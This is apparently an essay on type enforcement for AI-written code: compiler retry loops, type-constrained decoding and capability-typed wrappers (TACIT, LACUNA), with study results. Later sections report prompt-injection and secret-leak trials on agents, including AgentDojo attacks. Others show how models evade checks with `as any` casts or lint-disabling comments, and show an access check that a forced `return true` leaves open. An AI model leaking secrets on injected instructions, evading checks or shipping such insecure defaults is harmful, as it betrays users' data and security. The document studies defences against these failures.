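The simplest way to enforce types is to compile the model's code, return any errors to the model and ask it to try again. TypePilot does not include this step, although coding agents now do it routinely.

*Type-Constrained Code Generation with Language Models* (Mündler, He and colleagues, 2025) tested how well six open models could repair code in a single retry. Each model was given 292 short TypeScript programs that had failed to compile, with the compiler's message for each, and had one chance to fix each program. Gemma 2 2B, the smallest model, failed to get 194 of the programs to compile, while Qwen2.5 32B failed on 36. Of the 256 programs that Qwen got to compile, about 191 also passed their tests, and the other 65 or so gave wrong answers.

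Armin Ronacher, who created the Python web framework Flask, doubts that running type checks in a coding agent's loop is worthwhile. In *In Support Of Shitty Types* (2025), he reports that agents did worse with these checks. They would get their code running, discover the type errors much later and use up their context, the limited text a model can take into account at once, repairing them. Checking after every edit used even more context. Ronacher found that models handled complicated TypeScript types badly and Go's simple types well, and that plain compiler error messages helped more than a live connection to an editor's type information. The essay includes no measurements.

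Two later projects by researchers at EPFL, the Swiss university where Scala originated, provide some evidence. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes TACIT, a system in which an AI agent acts by writing short pieces of Scala that the compiler checks before they run. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) also lets the model's code control the agent's own loop. Both systems return the compiler's errors when a snippet fails.

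| System | Model | Task | Snippets rejected |
|---|---|---|---|
| TACIT | MiniMax M2.5 | Retail customer service | 0.33% |
| TACIT | gpt-oss-120b | Airline customer service | 1.58% |
| TACIT | DeepSeek V3.2 | Airline customer service | 7.93% |
| LACUNA | DeepSeek V4 Flash | Research questions | 8.6% |
| LACUNA | DeepSeek V4 Flash | Retail customer service | 22.4% |
| LACUNA | Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite | Retail customer service | 3.2% |
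| LACUNA | Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite | Telecom customer service | 89% |

Compiler enforcement added little overhead in TACIT. DeepSeek V3.2 had the highest failure rate, and each of its failed airline snippets took 1.39 more attempts on average, which added about 11 attempts per 100 snippets. MiniMax needed less than one extra attempt per 100 snippets on retail tasks. Compiling took under a second after warm-up, so most of the delay came from the model rewriting its answer.

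LACUNA's results are closer to what Ronacher describes. DeepSeek V4 Flash needed about seven extra attempts per retail task, and Gemini Flash-Lite, a small model, made little progress on most telecom turns because so little of its code compiled. The extra work the loop creates therefore depends heavily on how well the model writes the language. But Ronacher was describing long sessions in large projects with intricate library types, whereas these snippets were short and used simple interfaces, so neither study settles whether his complaint holds.

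### Errors that a model clears the wrong way

A loop that stops when the code compiles will accept `send(name as any)` as readily as `send(escape(name))`, so it enforces the type only if the project also forbids casts and `any`. For TypeScript, the linter typescript-eslint has rules that do this:

```js
rules: {
  "@typescript-eslint/no-explicit-any": "error",
  "@typescript-eslint/no-unsafe-argument": "error",
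  "@typescript-eslint/no-non-null-assertion": "error",
  "@typescript-eslint/consistent-type-assertions":
    ["error", { assertionStyle: "never" }]
}
```

The second rule matters because a value can have the type `any` even if the word appears nowhere in the code. For example, `JSON.parse` returns an `any` value, and the rule rejects code that passes such a value to a function. The last rule bans casts, so the file with the smart constructor needs an exemption. A model could also switch a rule off with a comment, but the linter ignores such comments when run with `--no-inline-config`.

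### Blocking bad code as the model writes it

Constrained decoding can prevent a language model from writing a program that would fail, instead of rejecting the program once it is finished. The model produces text one token (a word or a fragment of one) at a time. At each step it assigns a probability to every possible next token, and the software picks one at random according to those probabilities. Constrained decoding checks that token before adding it to the program.

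Let L be the set of programs that compile, s the text so far and t the proposed token. The software keeps t only if some further text r exists such that

s + t + r is in L

If no such r exists, it sets the probability of t to zero and picks again. The model can then finish only with a program that compiles.

An ordinary compiler cannot perform this check, because it judges whole programs and a half-written one is nearly always invalid. Mündler and colleagues built a special checker for part of TypeScript. One of their examples is a function that tests whether a text contains a whole number, and the model has written this much:

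```ts
function is_int(text: string): boolean {
  const num = Number(text);
  return !isNaN(num) && parseInt(num
```

Here `num` is a number, but `parseInt` requires a string. The table shows how the checker treats five possible continuations.

| Next text | Decision | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| `;` | reject | the bracket is still open |
| `ber` | reject | no variable is called `number` |
| `()` | reject | a number is not a function |
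| `, 10)` | reject | the first argument would be a number |
| `.toString()` | accept | the argument becomes a string |

A checker for TypeScript's grammar alone would have caught the first of these errors and missed the next three. Without constraints, CodeLlama 34B wrote `, 10)`.

To find out whether `num` can still become a string, the checker searches through types. It starts at the type of `num` and follows each operation that the language allows on it:

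```
number  --.toString-->  () => string  --()-->  string
```

The search reaches `string` in two steps, so the checker accepts `.toString`. Some searches would never end, because certain methods return functions that have the same methods. The checker therefore skips very complicated types, so it rejects some valid programs.

"Type-Constrained Code Generation with Language Models" evaluates six open models with 2 to 34 billion parameters on two sets of short programming problems. Failed type checks caused 94% of the models' compile errors, a figure GitHub cites in arguing for typed languages. When models wrote or translated programs, type-constrained decoding cut compile errors by 75% on one set and 52% on the other. Removing every syntax error would have cut them by only 9% and 5%. The share of new programs that passed their tests rose by an average of 3.5% relative to its previous value.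 Generation took 39% to 52% longer.

### When the checker is stricter than the language

These gains depend on how the researchers ran the comparison. Their checker does not cover all of TypeScript, so they kept every program that compiled without constraints and used constrained decoding only to redo the ones that didn't. The constrained version therefore could not do worse on programs that already compiled, and it got a second attempt at the others.

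In *The Alignment Problem in Constrained Code Generation*, Biagiola, Cesario and colleagues (2026) applied the same checker to every program from the beginning. They used the same six models and ran each setting ten times. The table shows their results on one of the two problem sets, with the models set to usually choose their most likely tokens.

| Model | Passed tests, free | Passed tests, constrained | Compiled, free | Compiled, constrained |
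|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemma 2 2B | 35.7% | 32.0% | 91.8% | 90.7% |
| Gemma 2 9B | 58.4% | 50.5% | 92.6% | 92.7% |
| Gemma 2 27B | 70.4% | 67.6% | 98.3% | 94.6% |
| CodeLlama 34B | 50.3% | 46.5% | 92.6% | 94.9% |
| DeepSeek Coder 33B | 74.8% | 68.0% | 98.3% | 95.6% |
| Qwen2.5 32B | 82.3% | 72.3% | 98.1% | 90.9% |

Every model solved fewer problems with the constraint, and four of them also produced fewer programs that compiled. The guarantee holds only for finished programs, and constrained models often reached the limit of 1,000 tokens or 300 seconds before finishing.

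The cause was the checker's incomplete support for TypeScript. Biagiola and colleagues ran their checker on 4,231 programs that Gemma 2 2B had written without constraints and that the real compiler accepted. It rejected 982 of them (23%). One rejected program called a helper function, `isPalindrome`, before defining it, which TypeScript allows. The checker blocked the name because the definition came later. When the model had to continue from `is`, it wrote `isNaN`, which has the right type but doesn't check for palindromes. In other cases the model repeated itself until it ran out of tokens.

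Training the models to write code that the checker accepts narrowed the gap. Qwen's constrained score rose from 72.3% to 77.6%, still below the 82.0% it reached without constraints. A checker that covers the whole grammar did better. For TOML, a simple format for configuration files, it raised Gemma 2 2B's share of exactly correct files from 31% to 48%. Qwen2.5 32B gained one percentage point, and Qwen3-Coder-Next, a newer model with 80 billion parameters, gained nothing because it hardly ever made grammar mistakes. When the researchers banned the optional space before the equals sign, that model's score fell from 62.5% to 1.9%.

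Constrained decoding needs the model's token probabilities, which providers of closed models generally don't share in full. A team using a closed model therefore depends on the provider to build in the checker, as some providers have done for JSON.

### A perfect check on weak types

Even a complete TypeScript checker would accept a greeting page that joins plain strings, because raw and escaped text have the same type. If `send` required a `SafeHtml`, the checker would reject `send(name)` and accept `send(escape(name))`, so constrained decoding could help with security once somebody had defined the right types. Mündler and colleagues' version could not do this, because it does not support programs that declare their own types, classes or enums. It also accepts `as any`, which bypasses type checks.

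A constraint can also force a model to fill a gap with an arbitrary value of the right type. In one of Mündler and colleagues' examples, DeepSeek Coder wrote a function that searched for a divisor and returned nothing if it found none. The checker required another statement, so the model added `return 1`, a sensible default there. Forcing a model to add a default would be riskier in an access check.

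```ts
function mayRead(userId: string, ownerIds: string[]): boolean {
  for (const id of ownerIds) {
    if (id === userId) return true;
  }
  // the type requires a return statement here
}
```

Both `return false` and `return true` compile, and the second gives every user access.

### The argument for hard constraints

*LLMs + Security = Trouble* (Livshits, 2026) argues that security rules should constrain the model while it writes code, because looking for flaws afterwards cannot be enough. Serious vulnerabilities tend to sit in rarely used parts of a program, such as error handling. A defender who runs an AI attacker against their own code has a limited budget and must avoid damaging working systems, while a real attacker can concentrate on one target for as long as they like. Finding no flaws is therefore weak evidence that the code is secure, since Livshits writes that "not found" often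 just means "not reached". Code that withstands today's models may also fail against next year's.

Livshits is equally sceptical of verification that asks developers to confirm specifications and settle doubtful cases, because people who let a model write most of their code tend to accept its changes without reading them. Livshits instead proposes fixed rules, such as checking bounds on every array access and sanitising every string that goes into a web page. Most security fixes are one or two lines long and stay within one function, so Livshits is hopeful that such rules can work locally.

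Livshits prefers diffusion models for this purpose. These models start with a rough version of the whole text and improve all of it over several passes. A model that writes from left to right has produced only part of a program at any moment, so a checker can't reject that part for failing to clean the user's input, because a later line still might. *Constrained Code Generation with Diffusion Language Models* (2026) describes a diffusion method that treats compiling, passing tests and satisfying security checks as hard constraints, and steers the model towards them with graded signals such as the share of tests passed so far.

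The difficulty with left-to-right generation applies mainly to plain strings. With `SafeHtml`, the code must clean a value before passing it to `send`, so the checker can accept or reject the argument as soon as the model writes it.

Livshits presents an argument but no experiment. Biagiola and colleagues' results give a reason for caution about that argument, because a hard rule that wrongly forbids valid code can lead a model to write worse code. Detection also finds faults that no rule covers, such as a mistake in the escaping function itself.

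### Types that people write and models use

A team can also choose the types itself instead of leaving them to the model. In the greeting example, a security engineer would write the `Html` object once and give the model only its function signatures. The compiler would then reject pages that skip the escaping, as long as the build also requires human approval for changes to the file containing `Html`. Google used this arrangement for its human developers. Odersky and colleagues ran the closest test with models, but their types protect secrets and do not address injection.

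An agent that works on a company's files may come across passwords or confidential contracts. The agent's model usually runs on another company's servers, so anything that the agent reads leaves the building, and a mistake or a malicious instruction hidden in a document could send it elsewhere too. TACIT therefore gives the agent secret data only inside a wrapper. In simplified form, it looks like this:

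```scala
class Classified[T]:
  def map[U](f: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

The agent can pass a function to `map`, which applies it to the secret and wraps the result again. In ordinary Scala, that function could also write the secret to a file. The type `T -> U` prevents this by allowing only functions that hold no capabilities. A capability is a value that lets code affect the outside world, such as an open file or a network connection. Capture checking, an experimental feature of Scala 3, records in each type which capabilities a value can use.

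```scala
val key: Classified[String] = readClassified("key.txt")

key.map { k => k.length }                     // compiles
key.map { k => logFile.write(k); k.length }   // does not compile
```

The compiler gives the second function the type `String ->{logFile} Int`, where the braces list what the function can access. Because the list is not empty, the compiler does not allow the function to be passed to `map`. This check needs no rule about passwords or log files.

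The design meets the same three conditions as `SafeHtml`. The agent lacks the permission needed to open the wrapper. Its code can reach files, the network and other programs only through TACIT's library. The compiler's "safe mode" rejects unchecked casts, reflection and the annotations that silence warnings, which could otherwise be used to bypass these restrictions. If the agent prints a secret, its model receives `Classified(****)`, while the user's screen shows the content. To summarise a confidential contract, the agent's code can call a second model that the company trusts, and the summary comes back wrapped.

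Capture checking can also limit how long a permission lasts. The `CanRead` permit from an earlier section stayed valid even if the program kept it for a day. In TACIT, the agent gets access to a folder only inside a block of code.

```scala
val later = requestFileSystem("/data"): fs =>
  () => fs.access("report.txt").read()   // does not compile
```

The block returns a function that would read the file after the block ends. The function's type would have to include `fs`, which does not exist outside the block, so the compiler rejects the code.

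### What the wrapper achieved

Odersky and colleagues compared the wrapper with plain strings in a sample project that contained secrets. For each model, 120 trials combined ordinary tasks with misleading instructions hidden in the files, and in another 11 the user asked for secrets directly. The table shows the number of trials in which a secret appeared in the agent's output.

| Model | Kind of trial | Leaks with the wrapper | Leaks with plain strings |
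|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | hidden instructions (120) | 0 | 0 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | direct requests (11) | 0 | 2 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | hidden instructions (120) | 0 | 3 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | direct requests (11) | 0 | 8 |

Without the wrapper, 98.5% of Claude's trials and 91.6% of MiniMax's ended without a leak. These percentages are high largely because of the mix of trials, since MiniMax leaked secrets in response to 8 of the 11 direct requests. With plain strings, the outcome depended on each model's training, but the wrapper gave the same result for both models.

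The type system is designed to guarantee the zeros, so the trials mainly test whether the researchers implemented it properly. The agents could still do useful work with the wrapper. On the 120 ordinary tasks, Claude succeeded in 99.2% of trials with the wrapper and 83.3% without it, and MiniMax succeeded in 90.0% with it and 88.3% without it. Odersky and colleagues suggest that Claude's gap may come from their set-up, because without the wrapper Claude sometimes stopped to warn the user or ran out of time.

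They also tested whether writing typed Scala makes agents less capable in general than the usual method, where a model calls tools one at a time by sending structured messages.

| Model | Tasks | Usual tool calls | Typed Scala |
|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | Airline service | 43.8% | 45.2% |
| gpt-oss-120b | Retail service | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Airline service | 58.4% | 61.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Retail service | 75.1% | 77.5% |
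| DeepSeek V3.2 | Airline service | 57.8% | 58.6% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | Retail service | 74.6% | 75.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Software repairs | 43.3% | 41.7% |

Typed Scala did slightly better than the baseline on all the customer service tasks, which the researchers credit to clearer return types and helpful compiler errors. On the 300 software repairs, it solved 125 and the baseline solved 130. The models managed to write Scala with capture checking even though they had seen little of it in training.

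Results were less even on AgentDojo, a public test of attacks on agents. Odersky and colleagues used it to compare TACIT with CaMeL, an earlier defence that tracks data while the program runs. Only 1 of 1,926 attacks on TACIT counted as a success. In that case the agent booked the hotel the user wanted but quoted reviews that mentioned the attacker's hotel, which the rules allowed. Odersky and colleagues call the two systems comparably useful, but the scores vary widely. With OpenAI's o4-mini, an old model, TACIT completed 53% of the office tasks and CaMeL 81%. With Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT completed 64% of the travel tasks and CaMeL 1%.

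### Limits of the wrapper

The types control where data may go but do not check whether the agent's answer is right. They also do not prevent timing leaks, because code inside `map` can take longer for some secrets than for others. The compiler cannot control other programs the agent starts, so the researchers recommend a short list of permitted commands and a sandbox, which restricts what a program can access.

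The guarantee also depends on the compiler, TACIT's library and the trusted second model. The basic theory of capture checking has computer-checked proofs, but the safe mode built on it does not yet. Library authors can mark their own code as safe even when it uses forbidden features internally, and the compiler accepts the label without checking it.

Compiler enforcement also requires someone to write the types. TACIT's shared library is about 1,000 lines of Scala, and the interfaces for airline and retail tasks are a few hundred lines each. Writing them is much less work than reviewing everything an agent writes, but it requires a programmer who knows capture checking.

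### When the model also writes the control flow

LACUNA uses the same Scala features but gives the model more freedom. When a program reaches a call such as `agent[Int]("count the overdue invoices")`, the model writes code to produce the integer. The compiler checks this code as if a programmer had typed it there. The code may use only the variables and tools available at that point, and it may call `agent` again for part of the task.

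The compiler checks each snippet as a whole before running it, so a rejected snippet changes nothing. If a snippet takes 50 dollars from an account in its first line and has a type error in its second, Python would change the balance and then crash, but LACUNA would run neither line.

This safety came with lower performance. On 392 customer service tasks, DeepSeek V4 Flash solved 76.0% with LACUNA and 90.0% with the usual tool calls. The gap is about 55 tasks, though Zhao and colleagues call the results on par. Type checking alone probably does not explain the gap, since TACIT's models lost nothing on similar tasks. LACUNA also changes how the agent keeps track of a conversation, and Zhao and colleagues ran its models with reasoning turned off.

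LACUNA also let through a few more attacks than TACIT on AgentDojo, 8 out of 1,898. Zhao and colleagues explain that the compiler limits an agent to the permissions a developer has granted, but cannot stop a misled model from misusing them. For example, an agent allowed to send email can send the wrong email in well-typed code. They suggest adding refined types to the expected result, so that the compiler or a verifier could reject some wrong values as well as wrong types, but have not built this yet.
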